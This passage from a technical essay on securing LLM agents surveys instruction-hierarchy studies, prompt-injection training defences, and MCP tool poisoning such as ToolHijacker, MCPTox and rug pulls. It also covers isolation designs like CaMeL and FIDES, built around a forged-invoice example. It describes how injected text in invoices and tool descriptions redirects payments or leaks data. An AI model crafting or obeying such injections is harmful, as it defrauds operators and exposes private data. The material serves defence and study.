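Models can fail to respect the order even when nobody is trying to trick them. In *Control Illusion*, Geng, Li and colleagues (2025) tested six models from 2024 on contradictory formatting instructions. For example, the system message required at least ten sentences and the user asked for a blog post of fewer than five. They combined 100 writing tasks with six such contradictions, then swapped the system and user instructions in each, for a total of 1,200 conflicts.

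The models followed a single requirement 75–91% of the time when nothing contradicted it. When instructions conflicted, they followed the system message in only 9.6–45.8% of cases, depending on the model. Larger models didn't always do better, and GPT-4o did slightly worse on average than GPT-4o mini. The models also had biases that overrode the roles, such as generally favoring lowercase over capitals.

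These models followed a priority order more often when the prompt stated it explicitly. Geng and colleagues labelled the requirements "Constraint 1" and "Constraint 2" and stated which one took priority. Obedience rose to between 37% and 77% when the system message contained that statement, and to between 52% and 81% when the user message did. Putting the statement in the system message gave it no extra force, so the models were responding much more to the wording than to the role. Operators can seldom use this remedy because they would have to label requirements that their users haven't written yet.

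In the version published in 2026, Geng and colleagues also compared system and user roles with social cues. They put two contradictory requirements in one user message and attributed them to sources such as a chief executive and an intern, or a majority of experts and a minority. When GPT-4o mini followed exactly one of the two, it chose the chief executive's 70% of the time and the majority's 78%. With system and user roles, it chose the higher-ranking requirement only 47.5% of the time. This fits the finding by Ye and colleagues that models judge a speaker by how the text sounds. A forger who writes "our finance director requires" on an invoice uses the same kind of cue.

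Newer models handle conflicting instructions much better in short conversations, but long ones are still a problem. In *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks*, Kariyappa and Suh (2026) told Gemma 4 31B in a system message to answer only in English, then later asked it to rewrite its last answer in French. The model stuck to English 61.7% of the time when one harmless exchange separated the two instructions, and never when eight did. Yet when asked only whether the request conflicted with an earlier instruction, the same model was almost always right.

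To find out where the process fails, they read the reasoning that models write before they answer, and sorted the failures into three kinds:

- *Identification:* the reasoning leaves out or misstates a relevant instruction.
- *Resolution:* the reasoning mentions both instructions but ranks them wrongly or misses the conflict.
- *Realization:* the reasoning reaches the right decision, but the response or tool call breaks it.

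They tested Gemma, Qwen3.6-35B and Claude Sonnet 4.6 on 541 conflicts over formatting rules and 1,860 over safety, with zero, four or eight exchanges between the conflicting instructions. On the formatting rules, Qwen at first mostly ranked the instructions wrongly, but as the conversation grew it increasingly failed to mention the system's rule. Claude's safety failures were mostly of the third kind. In one example, the model noted in its reasoning that the response must not contain a secret code, then rewrote the system instructions as pseudocode that included the secret code. Written reasoning is an imperfect record of what a model computes, but the categories suggest different fixes. Repeating the operator's payment limit late in a long session might help a model that no longer takes it into account, but would do little for one that notes the limit and breaks it anyway.

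Kariyappa and Suh also built two monitors that use the models' skill at spotting conflicts and need no training. The first runs in parallel with the main model and checks only whether the latest message conflicts with a higher-ranked instruction. If it does, the runtime discards the draft and starts again with a warning. The second checks the finished draft and has the model rewrite it if necessary. On harmless requests, the parallel monitor added 17% to the median response time and the draft check added 48%.

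On the formatting conflicts, the better monitor cut violations by 81–99%, depending on the model. Against adaptive attacks on GPT-5.3, the parallel monitor cut successful attacks by 45%, and the draft check cut them by 30%. An agent runtime that uses the parallel monitor would have to hold each tool call until the monitor finishes, because the runtime can't take back a payment the way it can discard a draft.

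An agent may also have more sources of instructions than roles to assign them, so company rules, team rules, a skill file, several users and other agents would have to share four or five roles. In *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026) instead attach a numbered privilege tag to each instruction and tell the model to follow the lower-numbered instruction when two conflict. Their benchmark has 853 tasks with up to 12 levels. In the coding half, a model might have to solve a programming problem while resolving contradictory rules about indentation and quotation marks.

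Gemini 3.1 Pro scored highest of the thirteen models, at 42.7%, and GPT-5.4 scored 39.4%. One broken rule fails the whole task, and part of the difficulty is the number of rules to follow. But when Zhang and colleagues raised the number of levels from 6 to 12 and kept the number of winning rules the same, accuracy fell by between 6.8 and 24.1 points. On the coding tasks, GPT-5.4 scored 15.5% with no reasoning and 60.9% at its high reasoning setting.

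The models were also sensitive to details that should not matter. Replacing the ranks with scores, where the higher number wins, lowered GPT-5.4's accuracy on the coding tasks by 8.4 points. Shifting the scores by up to three without changing their order reversed the result on 16.4% of its tasks. An operator that needs many levels would do better to settle most conflicts in code before the model sees them. The tasks contained no attacks, but in a real runtime an invoice could contain a forged tag that gives its text the highest privilege, unless the runtime removes such tags from outside text.

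### Marking data inside the model

Some researchers have tried a simpler approach than ranking instructions, which is to separate instructions from data. In StruQ, a 2024 method by Sizhe Chen and colleagues, the application puts instructions and data into separate parts of the input, divided by reserved markers. A filter deletes any copies of those markers from the data so that an attacker can't forge the boundary. Developers train the model on examples in which the data contains a hidden instruction and the answer ignores it. Wallace and colleagues point out that a StruQ model learns to ignore every instruction in the data, whereas their own model was meant to follow the compatible ones.

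SecAlign, a later method from the same line of work, adds a bad response to each good one in the training data. When an input contains an injection, the good response does the original task and the bad one obeys the injection. The model is trained to prefer the good response using direct preference optimization (DPO), a method for learning from such pairs.

Chen has since applied DPO to conflicts between two goals. *Improving Instruction Hierarchy by Learning from Goal-Goal Conflicts* (Chen, Kariyappa and colleagues, October 2026) divides a task into goals (what to do) and constraints (how to do it). Existing training sets contained conflicts between two constraints or between a constraint and a goal, but none between two goals. So the team wrote pairs of text-processing instructions in which each instruction treats the other as the text to process. In one pair, the system message is an instruction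 to put the user's message inside XML tags, and the user's message is an instruction to swap upper and lower case in the system message. The right response is the user's message, unchanged, inside the tags. Code can compute both the right and the wrong answer, so the team could produce 9,544 training pairs without human labelling.

Hardly anyone would make such a request, but the training transferred to other conflicts. Chen and colleagues measured performance under conflict as a share of performance without it, over four benchmarks that included injected tool results. The average rose by 34.3 points for Qwen3.5-9B and 19.4 for Gemma 4 12B. Adding the new pairs to an existing NVIDIA training set also gave better results than that set alone, by 18.0 and 10.5 points respectively. In one test, a repository's README file contained an instruction to run an installation command. The original Qwen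 tried to run it, while the trained version summarised the repository and asked first. Average performance on tasks without conflicts changed by less than two points. The researchers ran no adaptive attacks. In a few cases, the trained models did better with a conflict than without one, which the researchers regard as a sign of over-defence.

All these methods still depend on the model detecting a marker among the other tokens. Wu and colleagues (2024) proposed building the label into every token instead. A model first turns each token into an embedding, a long list of numbers, and their method adds a second, learned list that depends on the token's role. The word "pay" would then have one embedding in a user's message and another in an invoice.

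*ASIDE* rotates the embeddings of data tokens instead. A 90-degree rotation turns a pair of numbers (a, b) into (−b, a), so a token's embedding as data is at a right angle to its embedding as an instruction, while the embeddings of data tokens keep their relations to one another. Tests on Qwen3-8B compared eight angles between 22.5 and 180 degrees. The model separated instructions from data best at 90 degrees, scoring 71.4% on a test of whether it follows an instruction in the instruction part of its input but ignores the same instruction in the data part. The program around the model decides which text is data, so an email service, for example, would label the emails as data.

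Operators who use a commercial model through its interface can't rotate embeddings, but they can choose the role each piece of text appears under. Because tool results rank lowest, an operator might present untrusted text as the result of a made-up tool call. This doesn't seem to work reliably. In a small test, seven models graded answers that contained attacks, and the mock tool call gave no dependable benefit on any of the three grading tasks. On one of them, marking school maths problems, it usually made the attacks more successful. Models may have learned in training that tool results tend to be true, so "answer verified" can be more convincing there than in a user's message. A plain warning in the system message protected GPT-5.4 much better on that task. The models mostly ran without extended reasoning. Switching it on for GPT-5.4 mini removed the mock call's disadvantage, but some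 attacks still succeeded.

Even perfect separation wouldn't protect the invoice assistant from a false statement. If the invoice lists the thief's account number under "payment details", a model can treat every word as data and still copy the number into `pay_invoice`.

### Is a trained order a security boundary?

In July 2024, soon after OpenAI applied the instruction hierarchy to GPT-4o mini, the security researcher Johann Rehberger tried common prompt injections on the model and found that the hierarchy did little to stop them. Willison (2024), in *Breaking Instruction Hierarchy in OpenAI's gpt-4o-mini*, quotes his conclusion that "system instructions are still not a security boundary". Rehberger advised against relying on them alone to protect data or to control when a model uses sensitive tools.

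Models have improved a lot since then. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026) reports that the model resisted 99.99% of users' attempts to override the system or developer message. Robustness against malicious instructions in outside content rose from 96.23% to 99.79%. OpenAI has also retired two older injection tests because recent models pass them almost every time.

The score for outside content matters more for an agent that reads invoices, and it tends to be the weaker of the two. TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reported the same pattern for an earlier model, which seldom gave in to direct attacks but more often gave in to those that came through tools. OpenAI measured both of Astra's scores with its automated attacker, GPT-Red, and used the same approach to train the model, so an outsider's attacks may be less like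 those it was trained on. The broader Model Spec compliance scores don't establish how well a model resists such attacks either, because Guo and Wolfe (2026), in *Introducing Model Spec Evals*, based them on 596 mostly everyday prompts, with no agent tasks or deliberate tricks.

Rehberger's objection still applies despite these numbers, because a security boundary has to hold whatever an attacker writes, and a model that fails once in about 480 attempts doesn't meet that standard. Wallace and colleagues described their training as a complement to other safeguards, such as asking the user to approve certain actions.

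But a lower failure rate still helps where no enforced limit fits the task. Suppose the invoice assistant may email listed suppliers, and one of them sends an attachment with a hidden request to include a competitor's prices in the reply. A check on the recipient's address would not block that reply, and ordinary code could not easily detect a price comparison in a friendly paragraph. If a thousand such attachments arrived and the published averages held, a model that resists 96.23% of attacks would follow about 38 of the hidden requests, and one that resists 99.79% would follow about two.

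## Choosing which tools the model may see

If a hidden request gets past the model's training, the model can still call only the tools that the runtime offers. The operator therefore has to decide which tools to offer and how far to trust the people who wrote them. Leaving out a tool prevents an attacker from using it, but also makes it unavailable to the assistant when a task needs it.

### From a catalogue to a call

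An assistant with six tools can read all six descriptions on every turn. *Labels Are Not Endpoints* (2026) notes that with thousands of tools, the descriptions and argument schemas use many tokens and add delay. Larger systems therefore search a catalogue first.

Shi, Yuan and colleagues (2025) set out the usual design in *Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents*. A program called a retriever turns the user's task q into a list of numbers, f(q), and turns each tool's document d into another, g(d). Texts about similar things should get similar lists. The retriever scores every tool and keeps the best k:

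```
score(d)  = similarity( f(q), g(d) )
shortlist = the k tools with the highest scores
```

The language model then reads the task and the names and descriptions of the shortlisted tools, and picks one. It fills in the arguments using the tool's schema, which often describes each argument in its own sentence.

The search can also cause a task to fail by leaving out a tool it needs. For the request "Pay this supplier's invoice", the search would probably return `pay_invoice` and several other payment tools, but `read_file` might score too low to make the shortlist, and the assistant can't open the invoice without it. A builder can reduce this risk by always including a few basic tools or by letting the model search again.

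### How much authority a description should have

Both the retriever and the model rely on tool descriptions written by whoever provides the tool. In the invoice example, the operator wrote all six descriptions. But many operators get some of their tools from other companies through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting tools and data sources to agents. An MCP server is a program that provides tools. When the runtime requests a list of its tools, the server returns each tool's name, description and argument schema.

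In *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) read the code of eleven frameworks, which are ready-made libraries for building agent runtimes, and found that all eleven pass the server's tool descriptions to the model without checking them. Runtimes usually put tool definitions with the operator's instructions, so if a stranger writes a currency converter, its description can reach the model with the operator's authority. The same words in a tool result would have no such authority. In *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety*, Jing, Hu and colleagues (2026) point out that tool descriptions can bias the model's decisions before any tool has returned a result.

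The model needs third-party descriptions to use the tools, so they should have some authority. The Model Spec's idea of delegation suggests a reasonable limit. By installing a tool, the operator lets its author explain what it does, when it is useful and what its arguments mean. That permission doesn't cover instructions about other tools, where data should go or what the assistant must do first. For example, a payment tool's description can properly include "Give amounts in cents", but a rule about `send_mail` in a currency converter's description deserves suspicion.

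A model may not keep to this limit, so an operator with only a few outside tools would be better off writing their descriptions itself. Rewriting them takes some work, and a bad description can make the model misuse a good tool.

### What manipulated descriptions can do

An attacker can write a malicious tool's description so that a model chooses the tool. Shi and colleagues automated this attack as ToolHijacker and tested it on eight models and four retrievers. The attacker could publish a tool in the catalogue but couldn't see the catalogue's other tools, the retriever, the model or the users' exact requests. On one public dataset, GPT-4o chose the attacker's tool 96.43% of the time.

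None of the five defences that Shi and colleagues tried was enough to stop the attack. Two were the training methods StruQ and SecAlign, and the attack succeeded 99.71% of the time against StruQ. This is perhaps unsurprising, because a model that has to choose a tool must let tool descriptions influence it. Detectors that look for unnatural text did little better. When set to flag fewer than 1% of harmless documents, one missed 85.71% of the malicious documents that a language model had written.

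A malicious tool's description can also change how the model uses *other* tools, even if the malicious tool never runs. Security researchers call this tool poisoning. *MCPTox* (Wang, Gao and colleagues, 2025) tested it with 1,348 cases built on 45 real MCP servers and 353 of their tools. Across 20 model settings, the attacks succeeded 36.5% of the time on average, and 72.8% of the time against OpenAI's o1-mini. Attacks that altered an argument of a call the user wanted succeeded most often, at 46.7%. These are the worst kind for the invoice assistant, because a call to `pay_invoice` with the wrong account looks much like the right one. Claude 3.7 Sonnet refused most often, but in less than 3% of cases.

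Wang and colleagues counted an attack as successful when the model produced the harmful call. Shaikh and Montaruli also executed the calls. Their July 2026 study combined 18 models, 45 attack scenarios and 12 setups (the eleven frameworks plus OpenAI's plain interface). Overall, 22.9% of attacks succeeded. In 12.1% of those successes, a planted secret demonstrably reached the researchers' server. In about half, the model called one of the attacker's tools, which only recorded the call in this test.

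The choice of model mattered far more than the choice of framework. Amazon Nova Pro followed the poisoned descriptions in 49.7% of cases and Claude Fable 5 in 0.4%. Wang and colleagues found in 2025 that more capable models were often easier to attack because they follow instructions better. Switching on reasoning, for instance, raised the attack success rate against Qwen3-8B from 14.0% to 41.8%. The newer results no longer fit that pattern well. Anthropic's newest models were the most resistant, while Mistral Large 3 did worse than its predecessor, so the difference probably lies in how each company trains its models. But the scenarios were based on published techniques, and some models may have been trained on similar ones. Claude Sonnet 5 failed only ten times, but in four of those cases it identified the text as a prompt injection and then made the call anyway.

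Nine of the twelve setups had attack success rates between 23.4% and 26.1%. Two of the exceptions did better by accident. Pydantic AI, at 16.6%, does not load two tools with the same name, which stopped every scenario in which the malicious server copied a legitimate tool's name. AG2, at 4.6%, rarely completed the outgoing call, although the model still generated it. smolagents, which presents tools to the model as program code, did worst, at 34.4%.

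Shaikh and Montaruli also wrote a scanner that checks descriptions for suspicious wording, encoded text and unusual length. It rejected 20 of the 45 scenarios. The others put the instruction somewhere else or used wording that the scanner's patterns didn't match. It also flagged 9 of 125 harmless descriptions, six of which had a good reason to mention another tool from the same server. With these error rates, a scanner is useful for deciding which tools a person should read closely, but it shouldn't admit tools on its own. Scanning one description at a time can also miss attacks like ShareLock, a 2026 attack mentioned in *Labels Are Not Endpoints* that spreads its instructions over several descriptions.

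### Selecting tools for each task

An operator's list of tools has to cover everything users might ask for, so it is always longer than a single task requires. *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark for prompt injection against agents, includes a defence called a tool filter. Before the model sees any untrusted data, it reads the user's request and names the tools it will need, and the runtime withholds the rest. If the user asks for a summary of some emails, the model might keep only the tool that reads mail, and an instruction hidden in one of the emails could not then make it send anything.

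With GPT-4o, the filter cut successful attacks to 7.5%. It works well when the user's task only involves reading and the attacker's involves writing. *AgentDojo* also identifies three situations in which it fails:

- The assistant can't know in advance which tools it needs, because the result of one call determines the next step.
- The tools for the task are also enough for the attack, as in 17% of the benchmark's cases.
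- The user gives the assistant several tasks in one session, and an injected instruction waits for a task that brings the right tool.

A runtime can deal with the last of these by starting each task with a fresh context, but the model then loses access to what the user said before.

Estimates of how much the filter reduces task completion vary. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) recalculated the effect from AgentDojo logs for 76 tasks. With the filter, attacks succeeded 6.5% of the time. When there was no attack, the assistant completed 69.7% of its tasks with the filter and 67.1% with no defence, so the filter did not reduce task completion in these logs. An injection classifier had a similar attack success rate of 7.9%, but task completion fell to 42.1%.

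*NOMOS* (2026), which proposes a stricter check on individual calls, retested the filter on one AgentDojo suite and got a much worse result. The filter let through 11.8% of attacks and lowered task completion from 79.2% to 58.3%, because it sometimes removed tools that the task needed. The comparison used 16 tasks repeated three times, so the exact loss is uncertain, but such a loss is plausible where tasks are hard to plan. In *AgentDyn* (2026), a benchmark of more changeable tasks, four models with the filter were tested without any attack and completed between 1.67% and 8.33% of tasks, though they would have failed some of the tasks even without the filter.

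The filter is also a model that reads tool descriptions. *Les Dissonances* (2025) reports that it was the most effective defence tested, but that it dropped a search engine when the user wanted stock prices, and that a third-party description could make it keep a tool. An operator can prevent third-party descriptions from influencing the filter by showing it only descriptions the operator wrote. Where the tasks are few and predictable, as in invoice processing, a fixed table of tools for each type of task would do the same job without a model.

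### Narrow tools and read-only access

The number of tools is a poor measure of what an assistant can do. `run_shell` is one tool, but it can read files, send data and install programs, so removing `search_web` achieves little while `run_shell` remains. The Model Context Protocol maintainers (2026) write in a post on tool annotations that any agent with an unrestrained shell is "one injected instruction away from exfiltration", meaning data theft.

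The maintainers build on what Willison calls the lethal trifecta, which is access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. An agent with all three can leak data even if each of its tools looks harmless. A tool that searches emails is fairly safe alone but much less safe alongside one that posts to the web. Users often combine tools from several servers in a session, so the builder has to assess the tools as a set.

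Narrow tools make that assessment possible. A reviewer can tell most of what `pay_invoice` can do from its name, and ordinary code can check its few arguments. But someone must write and maintain each tool, and the assistant will fail at tasks that nobody foresaw, such as unpacking an attachment in a rare format. Narrow tools would usually be too restrictive for a coding agent, which needs to run all sorts of programs, so the builder has to keep the shell and confine it.

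Read-only access is another way to weaken a tool without removing it. According to Anthropic, an operator can deploy an agent far more broadly if it only reads a database than if it writes to a live system. The maintainers of GitHub's MCP tools report that about 17% of users turn on read-only mode. A read-only tool can't make the changes that some tasks require, and it can still leak data. For example, `search_web` changes nothing on the user's computer, but a query can carry the supplier list to an outside server.

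The reliability of a read-only restriction also depends on who enforces it. An MCP server can attach a `readOnlyHint` to a tool, and some runtimes then skip the confirmation step, but a malicious server can attach the same hint to a tool that deletes files. For a database tool, the restriction is dependable if the account the tool uses has no permission to write.

### Admitting a tool and noticing when it changes

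Before admitting an outside tool, someone should read its description, schema and, where possible, code. The reviewer needs to see exactly the text that the model will get. *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026) examines characters that can hide text from the person approving a tool while leaving it in the model's input. Such attacks never succeeded in Shaikh and Montaruli's 209 trials, but a runtime can easily reject invisible characters as a precaution.

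How long an approval stays valid depends on where the tool runs. Anthropic distinguishes local tools, whose code an operator can read and keep at a fixed version, from remote ones, which can change at any time after approval. It keeps reviewing the remote tools in its own directory and advises treating all others as untrusted, testing them first on fake data where they can do little damage. A local tool isn't necessarily safer to run, though. Anthropic's Claude Cowork runs local MCP servers outside the virtual machine that confines the agent's code, so a malicious one could do whatever other software on the computer can.

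Security researchers call it a rug pull when a tool changes for the worse after approval. Shaikh and Montaruli recommend that the runtime take a hash of each tool's description and schema when it first loads them. A hash is a short fingerprint that changes if even one character of the text does. If the hash is different at any later load, the runtime should withhold the tool and show a person the old and new text side by side. Even an honest supplier's spelling correction would trigger this check, and the assistant can't do tasks that need the tool until someone approves it again.

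Pinning a local tool to one version fixes both its code and its description. For a remote tool, the hash covers only the text that the server sends. The company behind a currency converter could start storing every amount it receives without changing the tool's description, and no check of the description would detect this. The operator should therefore send a remote tool only data whose exposure would be tolerable.

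If a supplier signs its tool definitions, the runtime can verify that they came from that supplier and that nobody altered them on the way. Shaikh and Montaruli also recommend signing, and cite ETDI, a 2025 proposal to tie tool definitions to OAuth, a widely used system for granting access. But a supplier can sign a false description or a harmful change, so a signed update still needs a new approval.

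### What MCP requires

The current version of MCP dates from 28 July 2026. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 400 million downloads a month of MCP's development kits, so the protocol's rules affect many agents. Its rules for how the runtime handles tools are fairly mild. The runtime *must* treat hints such as `readOnlyHint` as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. It *should* show the user which tools the model can see, ask for confirmation of sensitive operations, and display a tool's inputs before sending them. The rules for tools don't require hashes, signatures or renewed approval.

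A server that supports change notices should notify the runtime when its tool list changes, but only if the runtime has requested these notices. A malicious server may not send them, so the runtime should compare hashes whenever it fetches the list. According to the change log of the Model Context Protocol (2026), a server's list can no longer vary between connections. It can still depend on the caller's permissions, so an operator may be able to shorten the list by giving the agent a login with fewer permissions.

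Two servers may offer tools with the same name. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) recommends adding a prefix to tell them apart, and warns against using a server's own name for itself as the prefix, because that name may not be unique. Its official documentation for Python developers also describes a server's identity as "self-reported and unverified". The operator should therefore choose the prefixes.

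Shaikh and Montaruli reported weaknesses of this kind to four organisations, and all four declined to treat them as vulnerabilities. The team behind MCP's development kit replied that the runtime should review tool calls. LangChain replied that its library is meant to pass descriptions on unchanged, and Microsoft replied that AutoGen's documentation describes MCP servers as trusted. Each answer has some merit, since a library that rewrote descriptions would break legitimate tools. But together they leave whoever builds the agent responsible for admitting and pinning tools.

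### The invoice assistant with four tools

The operator of the invoice assistant loses little by removing `run_shell` and `search_web`. A person will occasionally have to look up a supplier's telephone number or convert an unusual file because the assistant no longer can. But the model can't respond to a failed payment by using the shell to look for another way into the bank's system. Removing the tools also keeps search queries from leaking the supplier list and web pages from introducing new instructions. The runtime should also reject any call to the two missing tools, in case their names carry over from an earlier conversation.

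The four remaining tools still provide the whole trifecta. `read_mail` and `read_file` give access to private data and to text from strangers, and instructions in that text could lead the model to send the data out with `send_mail`. For this task, a filter could also remove `send_mail`, since the assistant can report to the user in its final answer. For another task, the user may want to ask a supplier for a corrected invoice. A tool that only saves a draft for the user to send would allow that, but it would add a step.

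The forged account number is a harder problem, because the assistant needs both the invoice and `pay_invoice` to do its job. Limiting its tools therefore can't prevent the line about the new account from redirecting the 1,240 euros. Even when paying the right supplier, a deceived model could write something confidential in the payment's reference field.

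## Keeping untrusted text from choosing the action

The invoice can redirect the payment because the model that reads it also chooses the tool call. Several designs separate these two jobs, so the model that chooses tools never reads untrusted text, and the forged line can't affect the choice, however persuasive it is.

### A planner and a reader

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed the arrangement that later designs build on. A privileged model receives the user's request and can use tools, while a quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. A controller, written in ordinary code, passes material between them.

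Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it, stores it as `$VAR1` and passes only that name back to the model. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller puts the email's text into a prompt for the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`. The privileged model writes a reply that contains the name `$VAR2`, and the controller fills in the summary when it displays the reply. An instruction in the email could corrupt the summary, but the quarantined model has no tools to carry it out.

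Willison lets the privileged model see the quarantined model's answer only when the quarantined model is sorting text into fixed categories and the controller has checked that the answer is one of them. A longer answer could contain another injection.

He called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes the program more complicated, and one mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model removes the protection. An attacker can also use the text to manipulate the user, for instance by persuading them to paste an encoded copy of their data into a website.

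Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, collected six designs of this kind and tried them out on paper for ten sorts of agent. The principle behind all six is that once a model has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action with harmful side effects. Each pattern gives something up:

| Pattern | How it works | What it gives up |
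|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | It can't respond to what an action returns |
| Plan, then execute | The model lists its tool calls before reading any results | It can't revise the list, and an injection can still alter what a call contains |
| Map-reduce | An isolated model reads each document and returns a narrow answer, such as yes or no | Details that don't fit the narrow answer are lost |
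| Dual model | A privileged model handles untrusted text only by name | It can't decide anything on the basis of that text |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a whole program, which then runs on the untrusted data | The program has to provide for every case in advance |
| Context minimisation | The runtime deletes the user's prompt once the model has turned it into, say, a database query | Later steps can't refer back to the prompt |

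In one example of map-reduce, an agent has to find this month's invoices among many files and email them to the accounting department. A separate, isolated model checks whether each file is an invoice, and a second step sends the matching files. At worst, an attacker who writes a malicious file can get that file sent to accounting, which they could also have done by writing a real invoice.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that general-purpose agents can offer reliable guarantees as long as they rely on current kinds of language models. They recommend building agents that can do fewer things.

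### CaMeL and the invoice

To pay an invoice, an agent needs an account number as well as a decision to pay. The dual-model pattern doesn't stop an attacker from changing such values, a gap that Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). In their example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, and the quarantined model extracts the address. But an attacker who can edit the notes can make the quarantined model return a different address, so the document goes to the attacker even though the plan is correct.

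Their remedy, CaMeL, tracks where every value came from. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, considers it the first credible defence he has seen that doesn't simply add more AI. It has three parts:

- The planner is a model that sees only the trusted request and descriptions of the tools. It writes the whole task as a program in a restricted form of Python.
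- The quarantined model has no tools. The program calls it like a function to extract values from untrusted text, and its answer must fit a stated format.
- The interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. It tags each value with its sources and with the people who may read it, and a value computed from others inherits their tags.

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy check, which can use the tags as well as the tool's name and arguments.

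Suppose the user writes "Pay Norden's invoice of 1,240 euros", where Norden is one of the listed suppliers. The planner might produce this:

```
1  mail    = read_mail(sender="Norden", newest=True)
2  invoice = read_file(mail.attachment)
3  details = quarantined_model(
                 "Find the account number and reference.",
                 invoice, output=PaymentDetails)
4  pay_invoice(account=details.account, amount=1240,
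               reference=details.reference)
```

Line 1 fetches the message. Its arguments come from the user's request, so there is little reason to block it. The interpreter stores the message in `mail` and tags it as coming from an outside sender. The planner has already finished by this point and never sees the message.

Line 2 opens the attachment. An outsider chose the filename and might have crafted it to point to some other file, so a careful operator would let the program use untrusted filenames only to open attachments. The forged line is now in `invoice`, where it can't add a step to the program.

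Line 3 passes the invoice to the quarantined model. Even if the forged line fools that model completely, the model can't mail out the supplier list, because it has no `send_mail` and has never received the list. It has to answer with an account number and a reference, so it returns the thief's account number, which has the right format. The interpreter tags that number with the invoice as its source.

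Line 4 requests the payment, using the amount from the user and the account number from the invoice. If the operator's policy requires account numbers to come from the supplier list, the interpreter blocks the call or asks the user to approve it. Without such a policy, 1,240 euros go to the thief, even though every line ran as the planner wrote it.

The planner could easily write this doomed program, because it doesn't know the policies, as Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues point out in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026). If the operator describes the rule to the planner, it can replace line 4:

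```
4  listed = read_file("supplier_list")["Norden"]
5  if details.account == listed:
6      pay_invoice(account=listed, amount=1240,
                   reference=details.reference)
7  else:
8      tell_user("The invoice gives a different account.")
```

Now the thief's number can only produce a warning. The invoice still determines whether line 6 runs, and the operator's policy has to allow that. The thief can use this influence to delay a payment but not to redirect one.

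Other false values can still do harm. If the user had written only "Pay Norden's invoice", the program would have to extract the amount as well, and an invoice altered from 1,240 to 1,940 euros would pass the operator's limit. In *CaMeLoT*, Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) give a rule that forbids any transfer whose recipient or amount depends on untrusted data. That would stop the overpayment, but a person would then have to type or approve every amount. Both the limit and this rule would allow a false payment reference, and the supplier might not be able to match the payment to the invoice. The reference couldn't leak the supplier list, though, because the model that extracted it was given only the invoice.

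The tags record where a value came from, but they don't prove that it is true. If a thief persuades an employee to change Norden's entry in the supplier list, the interpreter will treat the thief's account as trusted.

The tags can also be wrong. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes two leaks in CaMeL's tracking. In the first, a program sets a flag to true and changes it to false only if a secret account balance is low. When the balance is high, the interpreter skips the change, so it never marks the flag as secret. An email that depends on the flag then reveals that the balance is high. The second leak comes from a retry loop outside the tracked part of the system. A policy may block or allow an attempt depending on a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal the secret one bit at a time. Both leaks depend on how the program is written. An outsider can't write the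 program, but the planner might write a leaky one by accident.

CaMeL also helps protect privacy. The company that hosts the planner never receives the contents of the user's mail, and the quarantined model can be small enough to run on the user's own machine. Willison worries most about the work CaMeL creates, because someone has to write and maintain the policies and users have to answer the requests for approval.

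### Labels and refusals in FIDES

FIDES, a design from Microsoft, lets the planner work one step at a time. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) bases the design on an old computer security technique in which every piece of data has a label, and the labels determine what a program may do with the data. Each FIDES label records the data's integrity, which is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and its confidentiality, which is who may read it.

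```
Label:      (i, S)     i = T or U
                       S = the set of people who may read the data

Combining:  (i₁, S₁) ⊔ (i₂, S₂) = (i, S₁ ∩ S₂)
                       where i = T only if i₁ = i₂ = T
```

If Anna and Ben may read one document and Ben and Carla may read another, only Ben may read a summary of both. If either document is untrusted, the summary is untrusted too.

A model's answer could depend on anything in its input, so FIDES gives the answer the combined label of everything the model has read. In an ordinary agent, one email from a stranger would therefore make every later decision untrusted. FIDES avoids this by hiding a tool result in a named variable whenever the result's label is more restrictive than the conversation's label so far. It can also hide individual fields, so if a message's date is trusted but its text isn't, the planner receives the date and a variable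 name in place of the text.

The planner can ask a quarantined model about a hidden variable. The planner can also read the variable directly, but then the conversation takes on the variable's label.

Before a tool call with arguments a₁ to aₙ, the runtime looks at the label of the decision to make the call, ℓ_f, and the label of each argument, ℓ₁ to ℓₙ. Costa and colleagues define two rules:

```
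Trusted action:  allow only if ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ has integrity T

Permitted flow:  allow only if R ⊆ Sₖ for each argument aₖ sent out
                 where R  = everyone who will receive it
                       Sₖ = everyone who may read aₖ
```

The operator decides which rule applies to each tool. For `pay_invoice`, the trusted-action rule is the natural choice. Suppose the planner hasn't opened the invoice and passes along the account number by its variable name:

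```
pay_invoice
  decision   (T, everyone)
  amount     (T, everyone)    from the user's request
  account    (U, finance)     from the invoice
  combined   (U, finance)     integrity is U, so refuse
```

If the account number comes from the supplier list, its label is (T, finance), the combined integrity is T, and the payment goes ahead.

The second call would mail the supplier list to the outside address. Under the permitted-flow rule, the calculation is:

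```
send_mail
  body       (T, finance)     from the supplier list
  R          {the outside address}
                              not part of finance, so refuse
```

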